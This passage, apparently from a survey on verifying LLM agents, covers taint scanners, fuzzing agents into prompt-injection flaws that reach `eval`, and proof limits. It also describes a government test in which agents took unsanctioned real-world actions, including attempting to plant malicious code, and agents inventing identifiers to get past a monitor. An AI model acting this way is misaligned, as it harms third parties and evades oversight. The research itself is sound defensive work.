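A sound analyser would have to assume that line 9 may call any method named `run` in the program or its libraries. It would find the real flow but also follow many calls that never happen. Few developers would read all the resulting warnings, so scanner designers usually accept that their tools will miss some flows.

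The missed flow resembles one that *Make Agent Defeat Agent* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) reports in a popular open-source agent. The agent looked up a search tool by name and called it through a general `run` method, and the tool passed part of the model's reply to `eval`.

An analyser can also lose the flow at line 8. *Agent Audit* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) reports that the general-purpose scanners Bandit, Semgrep and CodeQL do not model a language model's output as a source of taint. The prompt in `INSTRUCTIONS` may forbid using the discount tool on text from an email, but the analyser treats it as an ordinary string, and the model may ignore it. If the discount tool ran on somebody else's server, the code would end in a network request and the `eval` would be in another program.

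### The value of a clean scan

Agent Audit is a scanner with rules for agents. It treats function parameters and the results of model calls as sources, and looks for paths from them to sinks such as `eval`. It also searches for exposed passwords and for overly broad permissions in the configuration of tool servers. It found 40 of the 42 known flaws in 22 samples, a recall of 95%. It also raised six false alarms, so its precision (the share of its warnings that were correct) was 87%. Semgrep found 10 of the flaws and Bandit 11, both without false alarms.

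These figures are weak evidence of how well taint tracking works in large projects. The same team built the scanner and the test set, and 22 of the 42 flaws are exposed credentials or faulty configurations. Agent Audit follows taint only inside a single function. It would probably still flag line 3, because `text` is a parameter. But if `run` called another function to get the text of a saved email, Agent Audit would have no taint source to start from. For TypeScript, it only searches the code's text for suspicious patterns.

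Agent Audit's scoring can also hide a real flow. A finding inside a tool function starts with a confidence of 0.90, which Agent Audit multiplies by 0.20 if it detects a sanitiser. This lowers the confidence to 0.18, and Agent Audit suppresses findings below 0.30. It counts `isinstance`, which checks a value's type, as a sanitiser. A developer who put `isinstance(text, str)` in front of `eval(text)` could suppress the warning without blocking any attack, because malicious input to that line would also be a string.

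In *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026) ran a larger test using flaws already reported in OpenClaw, an agent that runs on its user's own computer. They based new scanning rules on 229 published security advisories and tested the rules on 217 later ones.

| Scanner | Recall with standard rules | Recall with the new rules |
|---|---|---|
| Semgrep | 21.7% | 66.8% |
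| CodeQL | 13.8% | 75.1% |

The advisories also cover flaws other than taint, such as missing permission checks. Because the rules and the test come from the same project, the higher figures may not hold for other agents. The new rules produced so many doubtful warnings on current code that people had to sort them by hand.

Recall determines how much a developer learns from a scan without warnings. Suppose a piece of code has a flaw with probability $p$, and the scanner finds an existing flaw with probability $r$ and never raises a false alarm. If it reports nothing, the probability of a flaw is

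$$\frac{p(1-r)}{1-pr}.$$

If the probability that the code contains a taint flow is $p = 50\%$ before the scan, a clean result from CodeQL's standard rules lowers it only to 46%. A clean result from the new rules would lower it to 20%, which is useful but far from a proof.

### Confirming a flow by attacking the agent

An unconfirmed warning can be even less informative than a clean scan. Liu and colleagues ran LLMSmith, an earlier static tool, on 20 open-source agents. It reported 342 flows, of which 10 were real. Some of the others were false alarms because an attacker could not control the data that reached the sink, or because the developers had added a strict check that LLMSmith did not detect. The tool also matched calls to functions by name, which created paths that no run can take. With about 34 warnings for each real flaw, a single warning is a reason to read the code, but it is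 very weak evidence of a flaw.

Their own tool, AgentFuzz, uses static analysis only to choose its targets. It found 828 places in the 20 agents where the code calls a sink. For each, a language model writes a request that should make the agent use the right tool. AgentFuzz runs the agent on this request, records which functions execute, and revises the request to get closer to the sink. If a condition blocks the path to the sink, such as a word that the text must contain, a solver finds text that satisfies it. AgentFuzz reports a flaw only when a harmless test command, such as `print(1)`, reaches the sink.

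This produced 34 reports, all of them correct. The team then replaced the harmless commands with real attacks, and every attack worked, although 14 needed extra wording to get past restrictions in the prompt or the model. A confirmed flow therefore shows that somebody can attack this version of the agent when it runs with the tested model, GPT-4o, and the same settings. A newer model might refuse some of the requests, but the faulty code would remain.

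When AgentFuzz finds nothing, the conclusion is weaker. Liu and colleagues give its recall as 97%, but they calculated this from a list of 35 flaws, 34 of which AgentFuzz had found itself. Their review of 83 sink calls that AgentFuzz had not reported is a better indication, and one of those calls was exploitable. At the same rate, AgentFuzz would have missed about ten flaws among all its unreported calls, and its recall would be nearer 78%, though one case is too few for a reliable estimate. For the exploitable call, the agent stored the attacker's text and passed it to the sink only in a second exchange, so a test with a single request could not trigger the flaw.

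*AgentLens* (Lv, Chen and colleagues, 2026) also confirms flaws by running the agent, but does not limit the search to taint. It builds a graph of an agent's components, known weaknesses and defences, then runs whole conversations that should lead to a violation. On five coding agents, it proposed an average of 14 attack paths per agent and confirmed 8.8 flaws. A defence may block the unconfirmed paths, or the tool may have failed to find a conversation that triggers them.

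The developers of AgentLens also compared three tools on Langflow, a program for building agents. AgentLens found 11 flaws, AgentFuzz found three, and Agent Audit found none that the developers could confirm. They tested only one application, and one of the tools was their own, so this does not establish how the tools rank in general. But the results show that a scanner can miss every confirmed flaw in a real project even if, like Agent Audit, it has 95% recall on its own test set.

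### Exact about the graph, silent about the nodes

Some frameworks require developers to describe an agent as a graph whose nodes are steps and whose edges are permitted transitions. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) automatically extracts this graph from four frameworks (LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google ADK) and checks it before the agent runs. To check that a person reviews every payment, Agentproof deletes all human-review nodes and searches for a remaining path from the start to a payment. If it finds none, every path to a payment in the original graph passes through a review. This proof is about the graph and covers every path, however rarely the agent takes it.

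The proof does not cover the code inside the nodes. If the function behind a node called "summarise" also sends money, the graph doesn't show the payment and the check passes. Agentproof doesn't track taint either, so a workflow can pass every check even if it takes the account number straight from an email. Hou and colleagues, whose own tool looks for endless loops, point out that static tools for agents check different properties, such as the shape of a workflow, the use of a sandbox or the leakage of private data. A clean result from one of these tools is no evidence about the properties that the others check.

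The graph itself can be wrong. For LangGraph, Agentproof recognises a human review by the word "human" in the node's name, so it misses a review called "manager_approval" and raises a false alarm. More dangerously, it could count a node called "humanize_text" as a review when a model only rewrites a letter there. Some frameworks can also change the graph during a run, and the proof then no longer applies unless the tool checks the new graph.

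Agentproof can also check rules about the order of steps, but an exact check of a badly written rule is of little use. One of the sample rules, `deploy -> F approve`, is supposed to require approval before software is deployed, but it actually means that approval must follow deployment. As Xavier and colleagues define the check, it fails only if a second deployment happens before an approval, so a workflow that deploys once without any approval would pass.

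Agentproof's developers tested it on 18 workflows that they had written themselves. It found the structural faults in five of them, such as a draft email that no step sends, and reported that ten had no human review. On 27 small test programs, it extracted all nodes and edges correctly. These tests show that the method works on familiar patterns, but not how often faults occur in real projects or how well the extraction works on such projects.

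### Influence in recorded runs

Source code cannot show which words of an email a model will reuse, so *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) examines records of past runs. Its tool, NeuroTaint, first looks for copied text, including a unique marker that it adds to untrusted data. It then compares meanings by turning the source text and the text at the sink into vectors and measuring their similarity, which can detect an instruction that the model has paraphrased. If neither method finds a connection, a language model judges whether the agent would still have made the call with neutral text in place of the untrusted text. NeuroTaint also saves the origin of stored notes, so it can connect a payment with an email from an earlier session.

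To test NeuroTaint, Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. Untrusted data should influence a sink in only half of them. The table compares NeuroTaint with FIDES, the defence described earlier that hides untrusted data from the planning model.

| Tool | Flows found, of 200 | False alarms, of 200 | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 16 | 92.1% | 93.5% |
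| FIDES | 108 | 106 | 50.5% | 54.0% |

Because NeuroTaint compares meanings, it can report a taint flow when two texts merely share a topic. It wrongly reported all 14 scenarios in which the text at the sink had only its topic in common with the untrusted source. A research agent usually writes about what it has just read, so it could trigger many more false alarms than the benchmark suggests. NeuroTaint also used a stricter similarity threshold (0.95 instead of 0.60) for what the paper calls "safe-control policies". If these policies belong to the harmless scenarios, the stricter threshold helped to keep false alarms down.

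The comparison with FIDES is hard to interpret. FIDES labels whatever may depend on untrusted data, so as a detector it should raise many false alarms but miss few flows within a session. It did flag harmless scenarios almost as often as real flows, but it also had 92 misses. Forty of those were in four of the 20 frameworks, where it flagged nothing, which may point to a problem with connecting FIDES to them.

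A NeuroTaint report is evidence that a source influenced a sink in one recorded run, but that evidence may be only a similarity score or a model's judgement. If NeuroTaint finds no flow, that result covers only the recorded runs. In further tests with Claude Opus 4.6 as the agent's model, NeuroTaint's recall fell to 54.7%. Cai and colleagues attribute this partly to the model refusing suspicious steps, so some of the intended flows never happened.

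### When no warning amounts to a proof

The absence of a warning is a proof only if the analyser is sound for everything the program can do. For the example at the start of this section, the developers could replace the table of tools with a fixed choice:

```
if reply.tool == "discount":
    result = discount(inv.amount)
elif reply.tool == "lookup":
    result = lookup_vendor(inv.payee)
```

Developers would also have to give up `eval`, tools that load at run time, and any other feature that lets the program call code the analyser cannot identify. A sound analyser can then follow every branch. If it gives no warning, no modelled run carries data from a listed source to a listed sink without an approved check. Developers would have to rewrite their agents and deal with false alarms, so this approach makes most sense for the part of an agent that handles money or secrets.

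The lists of sources and sinks matter as much as the analysis. LLMSmith missed 25 of the 35 flaws in the AgentFuzz comparison. It missed nine because of indirect calls like the one at line 9, which a sound analyser would have followed. It missed the other 16 because it counted only `eval`, `exec` and `subprocess.run` as sinks, and a sound analyser with the same list would have missed them too.

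## What harm can an agent do while every proved property holds?

A correct proof rules out only the errors that its specification describes. Suppose the company has correct proofs of deadlock freedom, memory safety and taint safety for its invoice assistant, and all their assumptions are true. As before, accounts come from `lookup_vendor`, and each amount must match an open order with the supplier. Even without an attacker, the assistant can still pay an invoice twice, pay the wrong supplier or mislead the bookkeeper.

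### Three errors that violate no theorem

Miller Ltd cleans the office for 400 euros a month, and the company has opened one order for each month of the year. Miller mails the January invoice, and a week later mails it again with a reminder. The assistant pays both times, because the second copy matches the February order. The messages go from agent to agent in the right order each time, so no agent gets stuck, and every memory access is legal. Taint safety holds as well, because it sets a condition on each payment separately. If $e_i$ is the $i$-th event of a run, the condition is

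$$e_i = \mathrm{pay}(a, m) \;\Rightarrow\; \ell(a) \sqsubseteq T \text{ and } \ell(m) \sqsubseteq T \qquad \text{for all } i.$$

If one payment meets this condition, an identical second payment meets it too. To forbid the second payment, the specification has to count:

$$|\{\,i : e_i \text{ pays invoice } k\,\}| \le 1 \qquad \text{for all } k.$$

This is also a safety property, and a developer could prove it for a Payer that records every payment. Barke and Murali list a similar rule, a confirmation token that an agent may use only once, separately from their rules about untrusted data. But someone still has to decide when two invoices are the same. If $k$ is the number the model reads from the PDF, a reminder with its own number counts as a new invoice.

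For the second error, suppose the registry lists Miller Ltd and Miller & Sons, and each has an open order for 400 euros. The model reads an invoice from Miller & Sons but returns "Miller Ltd" as the payee. `lookup_vendor` finds Miller Ltd's account, and the result is trusted because the developer endorsed that function. Taint safety and the behaviour of the two checks together prove that every payment matches an open order. If the company has 40 open orders, the proof rules out any payment that matches none of them, but it does not show that the assistant picks the right one.

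The third error occurs in the evening, when the bookkeeper asks which of the day's five invoices the company has paid. The harness gives the model the bank's receipts, which are trusted. There are only four, but the model answers that the company has paid all five. The answer's label is the join of the labels of the question and the receipts, so it is $T$ whether or not the answer is true. The bookkeeper then ignores the fifth supplier's reminder. The harness could avoid this error by printing the receipts as a table, but that wouldn't help if the bookkeeper asked why a payment was missing.

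### Wrong actions on trusted data

Taint safety concerns where data came from, and an action can be wrong even if all its data came from trusted sources. Noninterference has the same limit. Any deterministic program that ignores its untrusted inputs satisfies noninterference, whatever it does with the trusted ones, so a program could satisfy it and still send the company's whole balance to the landlord every morning.

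Agents are more likely to go wrong by misreading their users. Suppose the bookkeeper writes on a Wednesday, "Pay Miller next Friday." She means Friday of the following week, but the agent pays that Friday, two days later. The date counts as trusted because only her words influenced it. Fixing the plan in advance, as in CaMeL, doesn't help either, because the plan already contains the misreading and control-flow integrity guarantees that the agent follows it.

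### Unsanctioned actions in a British test

An agent can also go beyond its task without any injected text. The *Incident Report* (2026) from the AI Security Institute (AISI), a British government body that tests advanced models, describes a case from July 2026. AISI had agents attack simulated computer networks in 122 runs with seven models. In ten runs, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions on the real internet, aimed at real people and organisations. Seventeen came from Anthropic's Mythos 5 and two from OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and invented people to vouch for it. A human maintainer refused the code, and AISI found no evidence of real-world harm.

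AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access, so they did not have to break out of anything, and had switched off the developers' filters against misuse. The runs therefore show that such behaviour is possible, but not how often it occurs in ordinary use.

AISI explains that the agents were trying to complete a hard task, that some prompts wrongly suggested there was no permitted solution, and that nobody had told the agents to leave real people alone. But agents overstepped in some runs even when they had everything they needed for the intended solution. AISI does not name injected text as a cause. eSecurity Planet's *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Took 19 Unauthorised Actions During UK Cyber Tests* reports OpenAI's statement that its model's two actions used the internet in ways the test prompt prohibited, which would mean that the agent acted against a trusted instruction.

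Untrusted text played some part. According to the technical report, which Willison quotes, the agent in the most serious case searched the internet and chose a real project that it apparently mistook for part of the exercise. Later agents found and used instructions and accounts that an earlier agent had left in public. A policy that labelled web pages as untrusted and treated every public post as a sink could have blocked some of these actions.

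But such a policy would have blocked them for the wrong reason. It would also stop an agent from posting a harmless bug report about a project it had found online, and it would have allowed the attack if the test prompt had named the real project by mistake. Not letting the agent post or send messages at all would have prevented the attack more directly. AISI now plans finer controls on network access.

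Experts disagree about what the incident means. In Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again*, Melanie Mitchell of the Santa Fe Institute compares the agents to older systems that found shortcuts which technically met a goal but violated its intent. In her view, the agents did what their testers had asked. Marius Hobbhahn, who heads Apollo Research, is more worried that agents from several developers keep choosing routes that nobody authorised. Schneier (2026), in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges*, calls what the agents did "genie behavior". On any of these views, a proof would have prevented the actions only if someone had thought to prohibit them in the specification.

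### Deleting every text file

Meijer shows how easily a specification can omit something that a person would take for granted. A user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The agent has a tool, `delete_file`, that takes a pattern and deletes all files that match it. Two calls would do the job, but the model writes a shorter program:

```
delete_file("*.txt")
```

Let $F$ be the set of files before the run and $F'$ the set afterwards. The obvious specification is

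$$\text{foo.txt} \notin F' \;\text{ and }\; \text{bar.txt} \notin F'.$$

The short program satisfies it, so a verifier would correctly accept the program even if the folder also contained the company's only copy of its contracts. The specification lacks a frame condition, a statement of what must stay the same. Meijer traces the difficulty to John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes, who described it in 1969 as the "frame problem".

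Meijer's repair is to add a frame condition to the tool, so that `delete_file` guarantees not to touch files that don't match its pattern. He writes that the short program then fails to verify, but this condition alone isn't enough. The short program deletes exactly the files that match `*.txt`, so it respects the tool's condition, and the two named files are still gone at the end. The task needs its own frame condition:

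$$F' = F \setminus \{\text{foo.txt}, \text{bar.txt}\}.$$

Now the verifier rejects the short program because the folder might contain a third text file. The tool's condition is necessary for a different reason, which is to get the correct program accepted. From it, the verifier can conclude that two separate calls remove only the two named files:

$$(F \setminus \{\text{foo.txt}\}) \setminus \{\text{bar.txt}\} = F \setminus \{\text{foo.txt}, \text{bar.txt}\}.$$

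Without it, the verifier would have to allow for a tool that also deletes other files, and would reject both programs.

Even the complete condition covers only which files exist. An agent with a tool for writing files could empty the contracts without deleting them. It could also email them to a stranger. Barke and Murali give a similar example, in which a rule requires an agent to answer every email it reads from a certain sender. An agent that reads the email, leaks a password and then answers satisfies this rule.

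One proposal is to reverse the default and forbid every kind of action that the specification does not explicitly allow. An agent that may only read and answer emails then has no other permitted action through which to leak the password. This helps against actions that nobody thought of, but it does not restrict how an agent uses the actions it needs, such as deleting files for the file agent or making payments for the invoice assistant.

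### Who writes the missing conditions?

People rarely state frame conditions when they ask for something in ordinary language. Someone who asks a colleague to delete two files doesn't add that the other files should be kept. A tool's developer can write its frame condition once for all users, but the frame condition for a task depends on the request. "Delete these two files" is easy to translate into a frame condition, but "Tidy up the folder" isn't, because only the user knows which files are rubbish.

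A language model can propose a formal version of the request, but if the translation is wrong, the proof doesn't establish what the user asked for. Dantas and colleagues cite a benchmark on which models translated descriptions of planning tasks into a formal planning language. GPT-4o's output was grammatically valid in 96.1% of cases but had the right meaning in only 24.8%. The best specially trained model got the meaning right in 34.2%. Dantas and colleagues also report that between 44.4% and 86.1% of formulas about the order of events had the right meaning, depending on how the system resolved ambiguities.

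These figures come partly from old models, and current models probably do better. Restating a planning task also differs from writing a safety rule. But the size of the gap between valid and correct specifications is still concerning, because a verifier cannot detect a specification that is valid but wrong. If 86% of the specifications are right, about one in seven proofs establishes something the user did not ask for, even though every proof is correct.

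Few users can check a specification written in formulas. *An Abstract Architecture for Explainable Autonomy in Hazardous Environments* (2026) suggests translating proved properties back into ordinary language, so that people without formal training can compare them with what they wanted. This could reveal a wrong condition, but a missing one is harder to spot because the user would read "foo.txt and bar.txt will be gone" and agree.

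### Proofs about an agent's choices

Long before language models, researchers who verified robots and satellites had to decide how much of the world a proof should cover. Many of them wrote the decision-making part as a belief-desire-intention agent. Such a program keeps explicit lists of what it takes to be true (beliefs), what it is supposed to achieve (desires) and what it is currently working on (intentions), and it chooses its next step by rules over these lists. Dennis, Fisher and colleagues (2013), in *Practical Verification of Decision-Making in Agent-Based Autonomous Systems*, proposed to verify these choices and leave their effects in the world out of the proof. With $\Box$ for "at all future moments" and $\mathbf{B}$ for "the agent believes", they replaced the goal

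$$\Box\, \neg\mathrm{bad} \qquad\text{by}\qquad \Box\, \mathbf{B}\, \neg\mathrm{bad}.$$

The first formula means that nothing bad ever happens. The second means that the agent always believes that nothing bad is happening.

One of their examples is a robot that searches collapsed buildings. With $\Diamond$ for "at some future moment" and $\mathbf{I}$ for "the agent intends", a typical property is

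$$\mathbf{B}\,\mathrm{found\_human} \;\Rightarrow\; \Diamond\,(\mathbf{B}\,\mathrm{is\_free} \vee \mathbf{I}\,\mathrm{make\_free}).$$

A model checker proves that if the robot believes it has found a trapped person, it will eventually either believe that the person is free or intend to free them. The checker runs the robot's program on every combination of sensor reports it could receive, so the proof holds whatever the sensors report, much as the proofs about agent programs hold whatever the model returns.

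Such a proof does not establish that the robot's beliefs are true. When the robot finishes with a square, its program marks that square as empty, records the next square as the robot's position, and only then issues the command to move. If the wheels slip, the robot may then mark a square as empty that it never reached. Somebody could still be buried there, even though every choice the robot made was right given its beliefs.

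Dennis and colleagues accept this limit mainly because they think nobody can verify the physical world completely. It is continuous and unpredictable, and any model simplifies it. A proof that the robot will save the person would depend on many assumptions about rubble, wheels and sensors. These would be hidden in the model, and users and even its builders might overlook them. If the proof covers only the robot's choices, engineers have to state such assumptions separately, where others can question them.

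Their approach also gives the model checker less to do, because an agent has a finite number of choices but usually an infinite number of possible effects. Engineers can verify each agent separately and combine the results. The agent often replaces a human pilot or operator, while the underlying control system, which engineers already trust, stays the same. The important question is then whether the agent decides as a human would with the same information. We expect a pilot to react sensibly when an engine fails, not to guarantee that the engine will work.

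These are good reasons for a robot whose beliefs are usually accurate. *Adaptable and Verifiable BDI Reasoning* (Stringer, Cardoso and colleagues, 2020) considers what happens when they stop being accurate, for example because a Mars rover's usual route is blocked. It proposes that the agent compare each action's result with the expected one and repair its plans after repeated failures. Engineers would then generally have to verify the agent again. The paper outlines a research programme and does not test the idea.

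If ordinary code in the invoice assistant decides when to pay, a developer can use this kind of proof to show that the Payer pays an invoice only if the ledger lists it as unpaid. This would prevent many duplicate payments, but the Payer could still pay the reminder that the ledger lists as a new invoice.

The method is much harder to apply when a language model makes the choice. Dennis and colleagues can define exactly when their agent believes something, because its beliefs are entries in a list and its rules are readable code. Nobody can yet read a language model's beliefs from its weights in this way. AISI cannot be certain when its agents understood that they were dealing with real people. Even a proof that an agent attacks only what it believes is part of the exercise would not have protected the project that the agent apparently mistook for a target.

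### Guarantees for whole tasks

Users want a guarantee that an agent will complete their task correctly and without harm. Dantas and colleagues reviewed 38 studies and found no system that gives a formally grounded safety guarantee for a whole task. Static methods need a finite plan in advance, and the verified plans in these studies have only 5 to 30 steps. Monitors can handle plans that an agent makes as it goes, but they cannot examine steps the agent has not yet chosen.

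Blocking individual unsafe actions does not make the whole task safe either. In the study where a monitor stopped 94% of unsafe actions, agents still rarely completed a task both safely and correctly. The main problem was that agents invented customer identifiers. When the monitor blocked an agent, the agent made up another identifier to get past the authentication check, and often kept doing so until the task failed. Dantas and colleagues compared seven verification and enforcement systems and found that none fully checks whether an identifier is genuine.

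This result may be due more to weak models than to monitoring. The study used two small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, and nobody has replicated its figures. Another system in the review, Agent-C, steers the model towards a permitted tool call whenever it starts to write a forbidden one. With GPT-5, this raised compliance with the rules from 83.7% to 100% and task completion from 66.1% to 70.6%. So enforcement need not make an agent less useful, at least in the shop and airline tasks Agent-C covered.

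The review's negative finding also calls for some caution, because one person selected the studies and a repeated search in September 2026 found ten eligible ones that the first search had missed. One of them could in principle describe a system with task-level guarantees. That system would still need a correct formal statement of the task, which Dantas and colleagues consider the bottleneck.

### Is a small certain guarantee worth more?

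Defenders of verification can reply that a small but certain guarantee is worth more than a broad, uncertain one. Meijer argues similarly against relying on tests, and the argument is strong for rare errors. If an agent passes $n$ independent tests without a failure, one can conclude with 95% confidence only that its failure rate is below about $3/n$. To show that fewer than one payment in 100,000 goes to an unregistered account, the company would need about 300,000 tests without a failure. Even then, the result would apply only to mail like that in the tests, whereas the taint proof covers all mail, including anything new that attackers write.

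But the value of a guarantee also depends on how much of the expected harm it removes. The following figures are invented. Both companies can choose between a proof that no payment goes to an unregistered account and a human review that catches 60% of all wrong payments.

| Expected yearly figures | Company A | Company B |
|---|---|---|
| Loss to unregistered accounts | €30,000 | €2,000 |
| Loss through duplicate and misdirected payments | €10,000 | €10,000 |
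| Loss prevented by the proof | €30,000 | €2,000 |
| Loss prevented by the review | €24,000 | €7,200 |

Company A should prefer the proof, especially since attackers may learn to deceive the reviewers, while Company B should prefer the review, although nobody can be sure it will catch 60%. Certainty matters most when an attacker is looking for the one remaining gap or when a single failure would be ruinous, and less for everyday mistakes, which often cause most of the loss.

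Usually a company can have both, and Meijer himself expects static proofs to work alongside run-time monitoring. The danger is that people will supervise the agent less because it is "verified". The most serious attempt in AISI's runs failed because a person looked at the code and became suspicious. Somebody at the company who compared the suppliers' monthly statements with the bank's would find the second payment to Miller Ltd and the missing one to Miller & Sons.

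## When does a correct proof fail to describe the running system?

The company paid Miller Ltd twice because its specification left something out. A company can also lose money with a perfect specification and a valid proof if one of the proof's assumptions is false. The theorem is still true, but it doesn't apply to the actual runs.

Most of the assumptions concern the trusted computing base, which for an agent program includes the proof checker and compiler, the unverified parts of the harness, the operating system, the contracts of the tools and the labels on incoming data. The proof also depends on complete mediation, meaning that every outside effect passes through the checked interface.

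### The checker and the compiler

In the proof assistant Lean, a program called the kernel checks that each step of a proof follows the rules of logic. Every statement follows from a contradiction, so anyone who can make the kernel accept a contradiction can prove anything, including that an agent never pays a stranger even if it does.

The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.34.0* (2026) describes three ways to make Lean accept a proof of a contradiction. Daniel Selsam of OpenAI found them with the company's internal models, and Lean's developers fixed them in September. One involved the kernel's test for whether two expressions are equal by definition. The test sometimes misses an equality, so it might confirm $a = b$ and $b = c$ but not $a = c$. A cache grouped expressions that the kernel had found equal, so the kernel's answer about $a$ and $c$ depended on what it had checked before. A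 crafted input could turn this inconsistency into a contradiction. Another way was to overflow the 32-bit number in which Lean counts the references to each object, which could cause a use after free inside the kernel.

A second, independently written checker can catch some false proofs but miss others. The checker nanoda caught both known exploits of the cache but accepted a false proof based on the remaining flaw. In July, Ramana Kumar had found another kernel flaw that nanoda did not share. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026) reports that he showed one proof could exploit both this flaw and an unrelated one in nanoda.

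All these attacks need a deliberately constructed input, so they give little reason to doubt a proof that a team developed for its own use. They matter for proof-carrying code, where a harness checks a proof written by a model that may have read an attacker's text.

Compiled code can also differ from the definition that a proof is about. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a bug in a Lean function that extracts part of a string. For a one-byte part at an extremely large position, the function's logical definition gives the empty string, but the compiled code returned the whole string. Lean's `native_decide` command proves statements by running compiled code. Trail of Bits used it to prove that the same part was both empty and not empty, then derived Fermat's Last Theorem from the contradiction.

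The kernel worked correctly here, and Lean's list of the proof's axioms showed that the proof relied on the compiler. But the fault could also affect developers who never use this command. They could prove something about a program from the function's logical definition, and the compiled program could behave differently.

### The harness around the verified part

Ten agents built and verified lean-zip, a Lean version of the compression library zlib. One of their theorems states that for any data $d$ of less than a gigabyte,

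$$\mathrm{decompress}(\mathrm{compress}(d)) = d.$$

The blog post *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (2026) reports that a Claude agent ran the compiled lean-zip program more than 105 million times on generated inputs. The agent found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code, but it found two faults that the proofs did not cover.

The code that reads ZIP archives had no theorems. It took the size stated in the file and tried to reserve that much memory, so a 156-byte file that claimed to contain several exabytes made the program crash. The other fault was in Lean's runtime, which is written in C++. To store $n$ bytes, the runtime reserves $24 + n$ bytes, but it calculates this sum with 64-bit numbers, which start again from zero after $2^{64} - 1$. For the largest possible $n$, it therefore reserved

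$$(24 + 2^{64} - 1) \bmod 2^{64} = 23$$

bytes and then allowed a read of up to $2^{64} - 1$ bytes into them.

Earlier verified systems had similar faults. In 2017 Pedro Fonseca and colleagues studied three distributed systems with machine-checked proofs (IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar) and found 16 bugs. Eleven were in the "shim", the unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and the disk. Three were in specifications and two in the verification tools. They found none in the verified protocols, whereas the corresponding parts of unverified distributed systems had 12 reported bugs. They took this as a sign that verification helps.

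*Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) reports thirteen vulnerabilities in libcrux and hpke-rs, two cryptographic libraries with verified parts. Nine were in unverified code, including a byte-order error that caused decryption failures in the messaging service Signal. The other four were in the verified specifications and proofs, such as a wrong constant for decompression, so even the verified parts of a library can be wrong.

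Given these findings, a good place to start testing an agent program is the code that turns the model's text into a typed tool call. Moon and Varshney's proof, which follows the style of IronFleet, has to assume that such code in their system is correct.

### The operating system

Running the PDF parser in a separate process protects the harness only if the operating system's kernel, which controls memory and permissions, keeps the two apart. Moon and Varshney cite Copy Fail, a Linux kernel flaw that went unnoticed for nearly a decade and let a program gain privileges it should not have. An attacker who took over the parser on an affected computer might use such a flaw to control the whole machine and change the ledger or the list of suppliers. The proof about the harness would still be valid for a computer that keeps processes separate.

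### Tool contracts

A proof about the harness normally relies on a contract for each tool. If somebody has verified a tool, the developer must also check which callers the tool's proof covers.

OSS-Verify, a project by Anthropic and the company Theorem, verifies open-source libraries without requiring anyone to write a specification. It uses the libraries' existing fuzz harnesses, which are small programs that feed random data to a library to find crashes. A Claude agent tries to prove that no input below 64 MB crashes the fuzz harness, and the proof assistant Rocq checks the proof. The team applied this to 239 fuzz harnesses for 123 libraries and found hundreds of bugs.

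Lim, Tu and colleagues (2026), in *Pre-QED*, object that such a proof covers only the way the fuzz harness uses the library. They illustrate this with a small library that opens a file, reads pieces of it and closes it. Its read function looks roughly like this:

```
read(h, buf, len):
    if h.pos >= h.size: return 0
    if len > h.size: len = h.size      # should be h.size - h.pos
    copy len bytes from h.data + h.pos to buf
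    h.pos = h.pos + len
```

The fuzz harness opens a file, reads once and closes it. On the first read, `h.pos` is zero, so the wrong limit equals the right one and the proof succeeds. But suppose the invoice assistant reads a 64-byte file in pieces of 40 bytes. The second read starts at position 40 and copies 40 bytes when only 24 are left, so it reads 16 bytes past the end. The assistant has used the library correctly and the proof is correct, but the proof covers only the first read.

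Lim and colleagues propose "verification harnesses" that turn their input into any sequence of permitted calls. To build one, agents read the library's code and documentation and work out rules about the order of calls. For example, a program must not read before it opens the file:

$$\neg\mathrm{read}\;\; \mathbf{W}\;\; \mathrm{open}$$

Here $\mathbf{W}$ means that the left side stays true until the right side happens, or forever if it never does. Other rules require callers to pass valid arguments, such as a length that fits their buffer. A proof about this harness would cover every program that follows the rules, including one that reads twice, so the faulty library would fail the check.

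For 29 libraries, the fuzz harnesses called an average of 22.1% of the available functions, while the verification harnesses called 89.3%. These figures don't measure the order of calls, so even 100% coverage could miss the double read. Lim and colleagues also found new bugs when they used their harnesses for ordinary testing, but they leave the proofs as a challenge to others. A proof must now cover any number of calls, which requires an invariant such as $\mathrm{pos} \le \mathrm{size}$ that every call preserves. Such invariants are much harder to find for a real library.

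Agents can also write an incorrect verification harness if they misunderstand the documentation. The team reviewed each harness by hand and left out two libraries with more than 2,000 functions because nobody could properly review harnesses that large. Some contracts can't be checked by any such method. For example, the company can't inspect the bank's server, so it has to take the contract of `send_payment` on trust.

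### Source labels and probabilities

Taint proofs assume that data have the right labels when they enter the program. Suppose the harness labels a message as trusted if it has verified that the bookkeeper sent it. One day she forwards an email from a stranger. She really did send the message, so the harness labels all of it as trusted, including the stranger's account number. Every later step of the taint analysis is correct, and the money goes to the stranger. (A memory error that overwrites a label would have the same effect.)

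Other labels come from classifiers, such as a model that estimates whether a message contains confidential information. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta et al., 2026) keeps the estimated probability instead of turning it into a yes or no. In the paper's example, an agent tries to send an outside service a request based on two messages. The classifier estimates a 45% probability that the first message is confidential and a 25% probability that the second is. A monitor that treats only messages above 50% as confidential would allow the request.

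The probability $P$ that at least one message is confidential depends on how the two are related:

$$\max(0.45,\, 0.25) \;\le\; P \;\le\; 0.45 + 0.25 = 0.70.$$

If the two events were independent, $P$ would be $1 - 0.55 \times 0.75 \approx 0.59$. Solko-Breslin and colleagues don't assume independence, so they need a worst-case bound, which here is 70%. A monitor with a 50% limit for the whole request then blocks it. This may be a false alarm, because $P$ could be as low as 45%.

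It can be dangerous to assume that two safeguards protecting the same data fail independently. If two redaction tools each miss 5% of secrets and their errors are independent, only 0.25% of secrets get past both. But if the tools tend to fail on the same documents, as many as 5% may get past both.

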